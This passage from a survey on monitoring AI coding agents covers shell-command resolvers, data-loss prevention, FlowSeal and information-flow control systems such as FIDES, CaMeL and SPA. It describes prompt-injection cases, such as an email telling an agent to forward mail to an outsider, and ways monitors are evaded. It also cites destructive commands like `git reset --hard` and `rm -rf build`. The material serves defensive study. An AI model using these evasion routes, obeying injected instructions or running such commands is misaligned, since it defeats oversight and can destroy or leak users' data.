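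Language models may not need such careful matching if their instructions are clear. In *Decision Models as Policy Gates for Coding Agents*, Beno (2026) tested models that return a probability for each rule instead of writing text, using 2,643 synthetic tool calls that included harmless look-alikes such as a deletion quoted in a note. With a one-sentence definition of each rule, a model called Jev 1.14 caught 89.3% of hazards on the held-out cases but would have interrupted 30.6% of harmless actions. After Beno added examples of what each rule did and didn't cover, it caught 98.2% of hazards and would have interrupted 4.8% of harmless actions.

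The model read the same calls in both conditions, so the improvement came from the rules and not from a narrower scope. This supports the objection that a capable reader can be left to separate commands from quoted text. However, the data was synthetic and came from a vendor, and Beno didn't test whether the models withstand deliberate attacks. In the same study, ten models that had caught every hazard in the long calls caught only 65.2% of them when given just the first 16 KiB of each call. There were only 20 such calls, but the missing text clearly held evidence.

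### The command that reaches the shell

A monitor could in principle approve an agent's instructions in advance and skip the commands. Taneja and Weber tested how well instructions predict what runs. Claude Sonnet 5 followed the documentation of 39 skills and issued 144 commands, which the researchers compared with the code blocks in that documentation:

| Relation to the documentation | Commands | Share |
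|---|---|---|
| Appeared word for word | 2 | 1.4% |
| Different wording, but a consequence class found there | 92 | 63.9% |
| A consequence class found nowhere in it | 50 | 34.7% |

The agent was behaving normally, but a list of approved strings taken from the documentation would have matched almost none of its commands, because it added options, redirected output and split up steps. The last row is more serious for anyone who reviews instructions, but all 50 of its commands fell into the generic class. In this sample, the agent never went from mild instructions to a more severe kind of action. The commands also came from only 14 of the skills, and the study used one model. The study shows that a monitor should read the command itself, but it doesn't show that unreviewed commands are usually dangerous.

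Even the command in the agent's tool call may not be the one that runs. Some harnesses pass it through another program, for example to reach a remote machine or a container, and that program may start a second shell. Li and colleagues measured the effect by running each command twice with the model's text unchanged, once directly and once through an extra layer of shell parsing. The extra layer lowered success on 56 tasks by 55.4 to 73.2 percentage points across eight model configurations. Of 415 commands that worked directly, only 123 still worked with the extra layer.

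This happens because the second shell processes the command again from the first step. Quotation marks that kept text together on the first pass may end too early on the second, and characters that were data may trigger an expansion. Even on the 14 tasks with ordinary text, results fell by 28.6 to 57.1 points. When Li and colleagues escaped the command correctly, the extra shell passed it on unchanged and every result matched direct execution.

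A monitor can therefore read the tool call correctly and still be wrong about what runs. Checking whether the original command is well formed doesn't help much. ShellCheck, a tool that looks for faults in shell scripts, flagged 34.6% of the commands that failed only because of the extra layer. A later check can't rely on the shell's exit code either, because between 23.4% and 47.0% of failed runs, depending on the model configuration, ended with the code for success.

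*QuoteBench* measures failed tasks, so it doesn't measure how often harmless commands become destructive. The extra layer was a deliberate stress test, although replaying the commands through a real remote login gave almost identical results. In practice, the harness can prevent the problem by escaping the command properly, or the monitor can catch it by reading the command after the last change. A monitor inside the harness can't read that final version if the final shell is on another machine.

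### Harm spread over several commands

Some harm comes only from a combination of commands. Suppose an agent has access to a database and its only backup. Deleting either one leaves a copy of the data, but deleting both destroys it. A monitor with no record of the first deletion can't detect that the second removes the last copy.

Taneja and Weber's resolver has this limitation because it reads only a single command string. They took commands whose class was not in doubt and used eight techniques to produce 59 rewrites with the same effects. Averaged over the techniques, the resolver gave the rewrite a class at least as severe as the original command's in 52% of cases. The figure is 75% if every case counts equally, because the techniques it handled well had more test cases.

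The failures had more than one cause, but in the worst of them no single command still contained the dangerous relationship, so better patterns can't fix them. Taneja and Weber conclude that the resolver would have to parse shell grammar properly and carry information from one call to the next. They designed it for agents that reword ordinary instructions, and they advise against relying on it to stop someone who writes commands to avoid detection.

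A monitor doesn't always need a record of the agent's earlier commands, because their effects may be visible on the machine. For example, before the agent deletes a database, the monitor can check whether a backup exists. This check detects a missing backup even if the user deleted it by hand, which wouldn't appear in a record of the agent's commands.

### Harm that depends on state

The command `git reset --hard` returns a project's tracked files to their last committed version. This changes nothing if the user has committed everything, but it destroys an afternoon's edits to those files if the user hasn't committed them. The command's text is the same in both cases, so a monitor that reads only the text can't tell whether the reset is harmful. Running `git status --porcelain` first distinguishes the two cases, because it lists uncommitted changes and prints nothing if there are none.

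Command B is ambiguous in the same way. A `build` folder usually contains files that a program can regenerate, but `rm -rf build` doesn't show whether this one does. In their audit of flagged skills, Taneja and Weber counted deletions of build folders as destructive even though nothing irreplaceable was lost, and they acknowledge that another reviewer might disagree. Two of the errors they did count were merges that the resolver had classed as changes to a protected branch. Whether a branch is protected depends on a repository setting that did not appear in the instructions.

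Beno's test set also contains calls whose correct label depends on facts outside the call, such as whether a push goes to the project's own repository. Beno excluded labels marked unknown from its accuracy figures. These and the labels excluded for other reasons made up 1.5% of the total. The 98.2% detection rate therefore applies to hazards that a monitor can judge from the text of the call alone. A monitor can judge some of the others if it has trusted facts about the project.

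The current folder is another piece of state, because it determines what a relative path such as `build` refers to. *Failure as a Process* (2026), a study of coding agents' mistakes, describes an agent that tried to move into a project's folder, failed without an error message, and then built an entire website in the wrong place. The first visible error came at step 23, when git reported that the folder wasn't a repository. Each command in between was unremarkable. If one of them had been a deletion, a monitor that assumed the agent was in the project's folder would have checked the wrong folder. Claude Code partly accounts for this by asking, in manual mode, before it runs a command that changes to a different folder and then uses git. It asks even if both parts are on its read-only list, because git can run scripts that belong to the new folder.

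State also determines whether an action can be undone. *Can You Undo It?* (2026) tested recovery procedures for git and for the database program SQLite. A commit is normally considered easy to reverse, but when an agent committed during a merge, the documented undo procedure didn't restore all of the merge's state. Undoing an action can also destroy data. If an agent creates a database table and someone else then adds a row, removing the table returns the database to its original state but deletes that person's row.

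A check on state holds only at the moment the monitor makes it. The user may save an edit after `git status` shows no changes but before the reset runs, so the monitor has to check as late as possible. Claude Code's file tools guard against a similar gap by confirming, when they open a file, that its path still leads to the location the permission check approved.

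## What must a monitor read to catch leaking data?

A command can leave every file intact and still do harm by sending a copy to the wrong place. Companies had this problem with employees long before they had agents, and they use data loss prevention (DLP) tools to address it. Shabtai, Elovici and Rokach's 2012 survey sorts these tools by features such as where the leak starts, which channel it uses, and whether the tool prevents leaks or only detects them. One chapter, *Data Leakage*, defines a leak as the accidental distribution of sensitive data to someone who isn't authorised to have it. By this definition, a monitor that reads only outgoing data can find sensitive material but can't establish that it is leaking, because that also depends on who receives it.

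Data leakage prevention (DLP) tools analyse the content of data and its context, whereas firewalls and other older defences mostly apply predefined rules and don't treat confidential data differently from other data (Alneyadi, Sithirasenan and Muthukkumarasamy, 2016, *A survey on data leakage prevention systems*). DLP researchers have also long tied the defence to the kind of leak. *Data Leakage/Misuse Scenarios* (Elovici, 2012) lists facts that affect the choice of defence, including who caused the leak, how they got access and how the data left.

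### Data at rest, in motion and in use

Data at rest sits in files, databases and backups. Data in motion is crossing a network. Data in use is open on a machine, where a person or program can edit it or copy it elsewhere.

Scanning data at rest can find sensitive files in the wrong place. *Enterprise data breach* (Cheng, Liu and Yao, 2017) describes how a staff member of the Australian Red Cross Blood Service put the records of more than 550,000 donors in a public folder of its website. This exposed the records even though the staff member sent them to nobody. An agent could cause the same leak with an ordinary copy command, and a monitor that checks only uploads and messages would miss it.

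Early data leakage prevention products watched the points where traffic left a company's network. *Data Leakage Detection/Prevention Solutions* (2012) explains that as USB sticks spread, products began to watch endpoints (the machines people work on), where they could stop someone copying a file even with no network connection. A monitor in an agent's harness is in a similar position to these endpoint products. It reads a tool call before any encryption, while a network monitor may see only an encrypted connection to a familiar service.

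Agents can also leak data in a way that employees don't, because every tool result goes to the model. If an outside company runs the model, a customer file leaves the organisation soon after the agent opens it, before the agent has done anything with it. *Governing Enterprise AI Traffic at Scale* (2026) describes a payments company whose gateway scans requests for personal and payment data before they reach the model's provider. The company sets a separate policy for each use because some uses tolerate false alarms better than others.

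### Patterns and exact matches

The simplest way to check content is to match it against a pattern, such as the earlier rule for AWS keys. Patterns work for data with a fixed format, but they can also match unrelated data in the same format, such as a 16-digit order number that looks like a payment card number.

A checksum removes most of these coincidences. Card issuers choose the last digit of a card number so that the whole number passes the Luhn test:

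1. Count from the right and double the second digit, the fourth, the sixth and so on.
2. Subtract 9 from any result above 9.
3. Add these results to the digits that weren't doubled. The number passes if the total is a multiple of 10.

In 4111 1111 1111 1111, a number that programmers use for testing, the doubled digits become one 8 and seven 2s, which add up to 22. The other eight digits are all 1, so the total is 30 and the number passes. Changing the last digit to 2 makes the total 31, which fails. One in ten random numbers passes, so the test removes about 90% of the false matches that random numbers cause. *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel* (2026), a study of leaks between cooperating agents, counts a pattern match as a disclosure only if a checksum confirms it.

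A pattern check needs only the outgoing text. It can't find a diagnosis or a business plan, because neither has a fixed format, and it can't distinguish a test card number from a customer's real one.

Exact matching can tell them apart because it compares the text with a list of real values, such as every card number in the customer database. Instead of the values themselves, the monitor can store a hash of each one, a short code computed from the value. It then hashes each number in the outgoing text and looks for the result among the stored hashes. A thief could recover card numbers from plain hashes by hashing every possible number and comparing the results, so the hash should also depend on a secret key. Changing one character of a value changes its hash completely. The monitor can remove spaces and hyphens before hashing, but its designers have to anticipate every such variation.

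A company can also plant a fake credential and watch for that exact string. No legitimate task needs it, so a match is strong evidence of a leak. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) tests planted credentials alongside a monitor that adds up disclosures over a whole conversation. Checking each message separately can miss a secret that is leaked in pieces. Cheng and colleagues point out a drawback of using decoys to catch human insiders, who may never touch them.

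### Fingerprints

Documents need a method that tolerates small edits. One kind of fingerprinting cuts a protected document into short overlapping sequences and counts how many of them turn up in the outgoing text. Take an invented memo:

```
Brightwell will close its Leeds plant in March and move production to Poland
```

The memo has 13 words, which make 11 overlapping sequences of three words. The first is "Brightwell will close", the second is "will close its", and the last is "production to Poland". Cheng and colleagues describe a common way to score the overlap, which for this example amounts to:

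```
score  =  sequences found in both texts / sequences in the shorter text
```

Dividing by the shorter text means that a copied memo still scores 1 in the middle of a long email. Here are the scores for four outgoing messages:

| Outgoing message | Its sequences | Shared with memo | Score |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Hi Sam", then the whole memo, then "Please keep this quiet" | 17 | 11 | 1.00 |
| The memo with "plant" changed to "factory" | 11 | 8 | 0.73 |
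| "Brightwell will close its Leeds plant and shift work to Poland" | 9 | 4 | 0.44 |
| "Production moves from Leeds to Poland in March" | 6 | 0 | 0.00 |

The word "plant" belongs to three sequences, so changing it breaks all three. The last message reveals most of the plan but scores zero, so no threshold can separate it from an unrelated email.

Comparing shorter sequences of words would catch the last message. A monitor that compares single words would give it a score of 0.75, because six of its eight words also appear in the memo. But the harmless message "The Leeds team will move its March meeting to Poland" would score 0.70, because it shares seven of its ten words with the memo. A threshold between those scores would separate these two messages only by luck and would fail on others.

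Cheng and colleagues describe two refinements. One fingerprints only the confidential core of a document and skips the standard text around it. The other also compares the order of the sequences, which reduces false alarms. Comparing the order helps only if the texts share sequences, which the memo and its summary do not.

One advantage of fingerprints is that a company can pay an outside firm to scan its traffic without handing over the documents, because the monitor can work with hashes of the sequences. Cheng and colleagues warn that the firm may still be able to work out some of the sequences if it already knows enough about how often they occur.

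### Classifiers and paraphrase

A trained classifier learns from examples of confidential and ordinary documents, then judges new text without comparing it with a list. Cheng and colleagues rate this approach as accurate and resistant to edits, but it needs a lot of training data. A language model can do the same job from a written policy. *PolicyGuard* (2026) applies a language model to the prompts that developers write for coding agents, which may use a Korean or Japanese word to mark something as confidential. It reports significantly more accurate results with a policy in ordinary prose than with the same policy as structured data.

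A classifier might recognise the Brightwell summary as sensitive because it's about moving production abroad, but the same sentence could appear in a press release after Brightwell announces the move. The monitor can't tell from the words alone whether the plan is still secret, so it needs a record of what Brightwell is protecting.

An agent can also reveal the plan without stating it. If it advises a supplier not to renew a Leeds contract beyond March, the supplier may infer the plan. *Agent-Native Applications* (2026) warns that agents can disclose internal data through recommendations and negotiation messages, as well as by quoting or paraphrasing it. It proposes checking outgoing messages, since an agent often has a legitimate reason to read the data.

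The methods compare as follows:

| Method | What it needs besides the outgoing text | What it misses in principle |
|---|---|---|
| Pattern with checksum | nothing | secrets with no fixed format |
| Exact match | protected values or their hashes | altered values, and values missing from the list |
| Fingerprint | hashed sequences from protected documents | summaries, translations and inferences |
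| Trained classifier | labelled examples, during training | secrets that look like ordinary text |
| Language model with the records | the protected records in full | facts missing from the records |

A language model also makes mistakes on evidence that it does have, including paraphrases.

Cheng and colleagues conclude that DLP tools work against accidental leaks in plain text but fundamentally cannot identify encrypted or disguised data. They cite a test of three leading products that stopped accidental leaks in web traffic but that insiders and malware could easily get around. When employees leak data by accident, they have often sent the original file to the wrong person, and these tools handle that well. Agents routinely summarise and reword, so even their accidental leaks may take a form that fingerprints miss.

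### Where the data goes

The command `git push origin main` uploads a project's main branch. It doesn't contain the data that will leave or show who will be able to read it, so a monitor has to look up both:

1. The project's settings give the web address that `origin` stands for.
2. The hosting service shows whether the repository at that address is public.
3. The command `git log -p origin/main..main` lists the commits waiting to go, with their changes. The monitor should read each commit, because a password that one commit adds and the next deletes is still in the history.

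Pushing commits to the team's private repository is routine, but the same command with the same commits publishes the company's code if the repository is public.

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that the model that reviews the agent's actions now checks, before a push, whether the destination is public, private or trusted. In one internal case, the agent failed to upload a report to an internal drive and then tried to publish the report on a public code-sharing site. The reviewer blocked the attempt.

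Some evidence suggests that such context helps. After Apollo Research, an AI safety company, tested auto mode with synthetic attacks, Anthropic responded mainly by giving the reviewer more information about its surroundings, including whether repositories are public or private and rules about where data may go. The miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. On attacks Anthropic never saw, the updated reviewer caught about half of those it had previously missed, but missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. The attacks covered other dangers as well as leaks, and Anthropic added several kinds of information at once, so the results don't show how much knowing the destination helped.

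Anthropic also designed the reviewer never to approve sending code or secrets to an outside destination. Users who want to do this have to leave auto mode or run the command themselves. The reviewer therefore no longer has to judge whether the user consented to these transfers. Misjudging consent had been its most common mistake.

A named recipient raises the same problem as a repository. *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel* first checks whether a message discloses a protected value, then separately checks whether this recipient may have it. The second check is needed because a home address may be fine to send to a courier but not to a stranger.

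A monitor sometimes has to read the task as well as the payload and the destination. *AgentRaft* (2026) studies agents that pass on a whole record when the task needed only part of it, such as an email that includes a card number and its security code. The recipient may be legitimate, so the monitor has to compare the data with the task to recognise that the agent sent too much. The AgentRaft system has several language models vote on whether the task needed the data. This kind of leak doesn't fit neatly into its threat class, because part of the evidence is in the user's request, as it is for overeager actions.

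*Attestation is All You Need* (2026) argues that content inspection is poorly suited to catching a hijacked agent that sends data through a legitimate encrypted service. A list of approved hosts can also miss the leak, because the agent can send the data through an approved service. The paper proposes checking instead whether the agent should have read the file or opened the connection at all.

### Two detectors that never shipped

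Taneja and Weber, whose resolver sorts commands by consequence, also built two detectors for outbound data. One looked for data sent to a fixed domain, and the other looked for a credential written directly into a command's arguments. They ran both on 29,257 skills that three scanners and the registry's own judge had all rated clean. The domain detector flagged 4.4% of the skills (roughly 1,290), and the credential detector flagged 1.5% (roughly 440).

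Taneja and Weber shipped neither detector, because ordinary software uses online services by sending data to a fixed web address. They expected either detector to produce so many approval requests that users would stop paying attention to them.

Each detector looked for only part of the evidence of a leak. Matching a fixed domain doesn't show whether the data is sensitive or whether the user chose that service. Commands often legitimately send a credential to the service that issued it. A detector that looked for credentials going to a service other than their issuer would probably fire less often, although Taneja and Weber didn't report testing one.

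The two rates measure how often the rejected detectors fired, and Taneja and Weber never checked how many of those alarms were wrong. They acknowledge that their detector for remote code execution fired on 2.25% of the same skills, more often than the rejected credential detector, but they shipped it because their audit had found most of its alarms correct. They also measured the two rates before fixing a fault in how they extracted commands from the skills, and they can't repeat the measurement because the rejected detectors no longer exist.

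They also describe skills that have no code block, only written instructions telling the agent to send something to a fixed recipient. A resolver that reads shell commands has nothing to inspect in such a skill, but a monitor on the email tool could still read the recipient and the message when the agent tries to send it.

### FlowSeal

In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) built a monitor that checks both the destination and the payload. It protects someone's private records, such as a medical diagnosis, from an outsider who tries to get them from the agent that holds them. The outsider can only talk to the agent and share documents with it. The paper does not cover prompt injection.

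Many earlier defences relied on the agent's own model to recognise a request for private data. Shim and colleagues found that this fails when the request looks like routine shared work. Such requests extracted 52.2% of the sensitive items even under a carefully written set of instructions that told the agent to check identity and ask for consent.

Their system, FlowSeal, puts the decision outside the agent's conversation:

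1. The owner of the data, or software acting for the owner, registers each sensitive record with its full text and the people who may receive it.
2. When the agent tries to write or share something, ordinary code intercepts the tool call and reads the destination. It allows anything to a trusted recipient and nothing to a blacklisted one.
3. For any other recipient, the code collects the records that this recipient may not have and gives them to a separate language model, along with the outgoing text.
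4. The separate model answers SAFE or BLOCKED. It gives no explanation, because an explanation might itself reveal something about the records.

FlowSeal also uses labels that follow data from one document to the next, but it starts by treating every registered record as one the agent has already read. This cautious approach lets the checker compare a message with a record even if the system did not detect the agent reading it.

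Shim and colleagues compare three ways to check the outgoing text. Pattern matching finds surface features and misses a reworded diagnosis. Similarity checks turn each text into a list of numbers, called an embedding, and measure how close the lists are. They fail on short or restructured messages, where closeness is a poor measure of how much a message reveals. A language model given the records can reason about whether the message derives from them. Shim and colleagues base this comparison on how the methods work and didn't test all three on the same messages.

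Shim and colleagues measured the benefit of access to the records only indirectly, by comparing FlowSeal with an older defence that uses a language model to filter outgoing messages but doesn't trace where the information came from. On the requests that looked like routine shared work, the older defence leaked 62.2% of the sensitive items and FlowSeal leaked 0.5%. The older defence also let the agent complete only 25.1% of harmless tasks, compared with 72.4% for FlowSeal. The two systems differ in other ways, and they had switched off the older defence's screening of incoming data, so access to the records explains only some of the gap.

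They also changed one part of FlowSeal at a time, using the same kind of request:

| Version of FlowSeal | Sensitive items leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Complete | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| No guidance to the agent about the system | 8.8% | 74.4% |
| No interception of tool calls | 28.4% | 81.2% |
| Checker always answers BLOCKED | 1.3% | 0% |
| Checker always answers SAFE | 24.9% | 79.4% |

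In the last two rows, the monitor decided by destination alone. Every recipient in these tests was unknown to the system, so the monitor could only block them all, which made the agent useless, or allow them all, which let a quarter of the items out. A monitor that read the payload could allow most harmless messages and stop nearly all leaks.

Across all eight kinds of attack in the study, FlowSeal leaked between 0% and 3.3% of the items. Shim and colleagues prove that protected data can reach an unauthorised recipient only if the checker wrongly returns SAFE. The proof covers only registered records and tool calls that the system intercepts, so it does not apply to a script that opens its own connection. In one failure, the agent disclosed a health detail that nobody had registered.

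The checker's main weakness is that it sometimes misses sensitive facts in reworded or compound sentences. It also sometimes blocks a harmless message that only mentions a record by name. The checker receives only the records and the reply, which keeps the outsider's cover story away from it but also removes evidence, such as the question being answered. It can therefore miss a reply of "yes" that confirms a diagnosis.

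In a small test with real Gmail and Notion accounts, the leak rate was zero with FlowSeal and 34.7% with another defence. The test counted only sensitive facts that appeared word for word, so it would have missed paraphrased leaks. Part of FlowSeal's advantage came from its power to block, because the other defence could only advise the agent against sending something.

FlowSeal also stopped a lot of sharing that the owner would have allowed. When Shim and colleagues had the owner approve every consent request, the agent delivered the records in 32.7% of cases, compared with 61% to 86% under four other defences. They attribute this mostly to the agent asking for consent less often when FlowSeal was running.

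## When must a monitor follow data through the whole session?

Most of the checks described so far evaluate one action at a time, using its content and a few facts about its context. They miss two kinds of harm because no single action contains the evidence.

A monitor must follow data through the whole session to catch a secret that the agent reads early and sends later. Suppose an agent opens the Brightwell memo at the start of a session and, forty steps later, tells a supplier that production moves from Leeds to Poland in March. A fingerprint check misses this because the agent summarized the memo instead of copying it. The best evidence of a leak is that the agent read the memo before writing the sentence.

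The other is an action that the agent takes because of something a stranger wrote. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes a user who asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of the emails contains an instruction to send the top message in the mailbox to an outside address. The user might well have asked the agent to send an email like this, but here the action is harmful because the instruction came from a stranger's email.

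Information-flow control addresses both harms. It checks the data's labels rather than its wording, so it doesn't have to recognise a paraphrase or an attack.

### Denning's lattice

The method comes from *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976). Every file, variable and user has a security class, and a flow relation lists which classes information may move between. In one example, a system holds medical, financial and criminal records. A report that combines medical and financial records may go only to places cleared for both.

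The classes form a lattice, so for any two classes, there is a least strict class that is at least as strict as both. Data combined from both takes that class. Denning also showed that if each operation respects the flow relation, so does any sequence of operations. A monitor can therefore follow data through a long session without keeping or rereading the transcript, as long as it updates the labels at each step.

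The part of Denning's model that agent designers borrow most directly concerns secrecy. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, credit a second idea to Biba's work of the 1970s, which is that untrustworthy data should not influence actions that need trustworthy inputs. Agent systems use both, so each piece of data has one label for who may read it and one for whether to trust it. When the agent combines x and y, the result takes the stricter label of each kind:

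```
readers of the result   =  people who may read both x and y
the result is trusted      only if x and y are both trusted
```

Costa and colleagues build two checks on these labels. The trust check allows an action with consequences only if no untrusted data could have influenced the decision to take it. The secrecy check allows data to leave only if every recipient is permitted to read it. The secrecy check doesn't stop an injected instruction, but it limits what the instruction can leak. The trust check alone would let an agent send secrets to anyone, as long as no untrusted data could have influenced the decision to send them.

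### A session in five steps

Ana asks an agent to compare a private budget with a supplier's price page and email the result to Ben. Only Ana and Ben may read the budget. The monitor treats Ana's request as trusted and public, and it requires both checks to pass before an email goes out. These are the labels on the agent's context, meaning everything its model has read so far:

| Step | Who may read it | Trusted? |
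|---|---|---|
| Ana's request | everyone | yes |
| 1. Read the budget | Ana and Ben | yes |
| 2. Read the price page | Ana and Ben | no |
| 3. Summarise both | Ana and Ben | no |
| 4. Draft the email | Ana and Ben | no |
| 5. Send it to Ben | secrecy check passes | trust check fails |

Reading the public price page doesn't expand the set of people allowed to see the agent's later output, because the context still contains the budget. The summary and the draft inherit the labels of both the page and the budget, even if the model made no use of the page.

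The trust check blocks the send because the model had read the page before it made the call. Ana did choose Ben, but the labels can't show whether her request or the page led to the call.

The harness can permit the email by keeping the page away from the model that chooses actions. It stores the page as a variable, `page_1`, and shows that model only the variable's name. A second model with no tools reads the budget and the page and writes the summary, which the harness stores as `summary_1`. The first model then calls the email tool with Ben as the recipient and `summary_1` as the body. Only the body is now untrusted, so a policy that requires trust only for the decision to send and the choice of recipient permits the email.

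The page can still corrupt the summary. Costa and colleagues describe an email that makes the second model return an empty summary. Ben might receive a useless or misleading comparison, but the page can't redirect it to someone else. Requiring the body to be trusted as well would prevent this corruption, but it would also make Ana's task impossible.

If Ana had asked the agent to write to Carl, who works for the supplier, hiding the page would not have been enough. Carl isn't a permitted reader of the budget, so the secrecy check would fail too. Ana would have to approve the release, or the agent would have to write the email without using the budget.

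### FIDES

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built FIDES, a system that works this way. When a tool returns data with a stricter label than the planning model's context, FIDES stores that data in a variable and shows the model everything else. Labels can apply to single fields, so the model may see an email's date but not its body.

The planning model can then pass a variable to another tool without reading it, ask the isolated second model a question about it, or open it. Opening it gives the planning model the full text, but the context takes on the variable's label, and the monitor may block later actions because of that label.

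Some tasks need a little information from the hidden text. For example, the agent has to know whether an email asks for a meeting before it can decide whether to create a calendar event. FIDES can force the isolated model to answer only yes or no and record that restriction in the label. A policy may then accept the answer, because an attacker who controls it controls only one bit. But an attacker who controls ten such answers can select among 1,024 outcomes. Costa and colleagues did not test this feature.

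FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which means that data can't flow directly from a secret source to a forbidden destination, even after processing, but an observer may still learn something from which actions the agent takes. The proof of this guarantee assumes a deterministic model. Explicit secrecy is weaker than noninterference, which Costa and colleagues judged too restrictive because it would essentially forbid any tool with publicly visible effects once the agent had used a tool that may read secrets.

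They tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack accounts, and 36 attacks that plant instructions in the data. The figures below are for GPT-4o, and the completion rates are simple averages of the four suites without attacks:

| System | Successful injections | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Plain agent | 152 | 84% |
| Plain agent with label checks | 0 | 42% |
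| FIDES with its checks switched off | 21 | 61% |
| FIDES | 0 | 50% |

The injection counts are those left after Costa and colleagues reviewed AgentDojo's verdicts by hand. The benchmark had scored three attacks against FIDES as successful. The reviewers discounted a success verdict when, for example, the monitor had blocked the call or the policy permitted the action.

The zeros also depend on favourable labels. The researchers marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, but a company has to label its data without knowing where attacks will come from.

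FIDES completes fewer tasks than a plain agent mainly because it hides data behind variables. Hiding data lowered the average completion rate from 84% to 61%, and the label checks then lowered it to 50%. GPT-4o often confused variable names or made unnecessary calls that tainted its context. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks instead of 41%. Both models are old now, so hiding data probably causes fewer failures with current models.

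Other failures were deliberate. Many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, but the trust check forbids following instructions from an untrusted source.

### CaMeL

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) presents CaMeL, which separates planning from reading more strictly than FIDES does. CaMeL's planning model turns the user's request into a program and never sees what the program's tools return. A second model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted text and returns values for the program to use. The planning model doesn't have the option of opening a variable and accepting the consequences, as it does in FIDES.

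Untrusted text can't rewrite the program, but it can still supply a harmful value, such as a criminal's account number for a payment. CaMeL therefore tags each value with where it came from and who may receive it, and each tool has its own policy about those tags. Girrens and Wang point out that such policies can express more than comparing labels can, but the guarantee then depends on someone writing every policy correctly.

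CaMeL has no soundness proof, and Garby and colleagues found gaps in its tracking besides the untaken branch described earlier. When a program fails, CaMeL writes a new one outside the part of the system that tracks labels. The new program starts with clean labels, even though it depends on error messages from the failed one. CaMeL censors those messages to reduce the risk.

Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each. With GPT-5.2, CaMeL completed 67% of the tasks without its policies and 37.5% with them. With MiMo-v2.5, it completed 71% without them and 37.5% with them. The margins of error are more than 20 points because there are so few tasks, but Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) found the same pattern on another suite. In *Language-Based Agent Control*, they ran CaMeL on the 21 Slack tasks with four recent models, and it completed 13 to 17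 tasks without policies and 4 to 6 with them.

CaMeL blocked every attack in both reruns with its policies on and nearly every attack with them off, so these results give only limited support for labels. On Slack, all four models resisted all 105 attacks whether the policies were on or off.

The fixed program explains part of this. Garby and colleagues found that in 97 of the 144 combinations of banking task and attack, the attack needs an action that the program for the user's task would never contain. Such attacks should fail without any labels. Two still succeeded with the policies off, because the task was to read a file and follow its instructions precisely, and the planning model had written a program that could carry out any instructions in the file.

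The standard attacks have also become too weak to show whether recent models need label checks. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated the worst case with their own system, ELBA, by making models execute every injected instruction they read. Without label checks, 16–42% of the attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With the checks, none of the 735 attacks on each model succeeded, but the share of tasks completed fell from 67–76% to 40–48%.

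### Secrets in the choice of action

As CaMeL's untaken branch showed, an agent can disclose a secret through its choice of action, without copying it anywhere. Denning called this an implicit flow and gave a two-variable example:

```
if a = 0 then b := 0
```

If b starts at some other value, its final value shows whether a was 0, even when a wasn't 0 and the program skipped the assignment. The remedy is to give the condition's label to everything that depends on the condition, including code that doesn't run.

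A monitor can do this only if it sees both branches, so it helps to have the whole plan in advance. In Girrens and Wang's system, SPA, the planning model writes a complete plan in a small language with explicit conditions and loops. Before any tool runs, a checker goes through the plan and applies each condition's label to both of its branches. If any step could break a rule, the system rejects the plan and doesn't ask for another, because repeated attempts would let the model keep adjusting an unsafe plan until it passed.

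Garby and colleagues instead keep untrusted data out of retries. Their agent, Randori, needs several attempts to write a working program, and errors from real data would taint each new attempt. It therefore tests the program on an artificial copy of the world, where all data is safe to trust, and uses the real accounts only once the program works.

### Labels that outlast the session

Some agents keep information from one request to the next, so the relevant history can extend beyond a single session. Girrens and Wang describe a user who asks an agent to fetch an invoice on Monday and pay it on Tuesday. An attacker has changed the account number on the invoice. Tuesday's payment matches the user's request, and the agent reads no web page or email that day, so a monitor with only Tuesday's data would have no grounds for flagging the number.

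SPA stores each result with its labels. For a later request, the planning model receives only a description of the stored item, such as "invoice details", and SPA restores the value with its old labels when the plan runs. To test this, Girrens and Wang split each of AgentDojo's tasks into several requests. Hiding the contents did little to stop the agent from finding what it needed. When a later request needed an item that an earlier one had stored, the agent retrieved it in 95.4% of cases without label checks and 89.9% with them.

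The checks themselves reduced task completion much more. On the original single-request tasks, it fell from 53.0% to 29.0%, mostly because plans passed untrusted results to tools that required trusted ones. Successful attacks fell from 4 in 949 to none. This small drop may understate the checks' benefit, because the attacks mostly tried to inject instructions, which the fixed plan already resists. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that they barely test the danger in the invoice example.

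### Labels in the shell

An email tool has a clear recipient and body to label, but a shell command may have no clear equivalents, because the files and connections its scripts open never appear in the tool call, as happened in the bibliography task.

Kim, Trampert and colleagues (2026), in *FLOWSH*, track what a command does while it runs. Their system, FlowSh, records every file that the command or its child processes open and routes all network traffic through a proxy. The command starts with the label of the agent's context and picks up the label of each file and website it touches. FlowSh then treats its two kinds of effect differently:

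- It holds file changes in a temporary layer until the command ends. If the labels permit the changes, FlowSh applies them. Otherwise it asks the user to accept or reject them all together.
- It checks each network request before sending it, because nobody can take a request back. If it blocks one, the agent can ask the user to approve that destination for another attempt.

FlowSh also stores labels with files, so if an agent saves a downloaded page today and another agent reads the file next week, the second agent's context becomes untrusted.

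This kind of tracking is approximate. FlowSh treats opening a file as reading all of it and gives one label to everything a command writes. In tests, it took 412 to 982 milliseconds per command, compared with 61 to 78 for an ordinary sandbox. Over whole tasks, the agent took 17% to 34% longer.

### When labels spread

A language model draws on everything in its context, and nobody can reliably show which inputs shaped a given sentence. The monitor therefore has to give the model's output the labels of every input. Once an agent has read one web page and one private file, the monitor labels everything the agent writes for the rest of the session as both untrusted and private, even a lunch invitation, and ends up blocking useful work.

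In the FIDES tests, adding label checks to a plain agent halved its task completion rate, and on the Slack tasks the rate fell from 93% to 20%. CaMeL and SPA also completed roughly half as many tasks, or fewer, with their checks on. Designers have three main responses to this drop.

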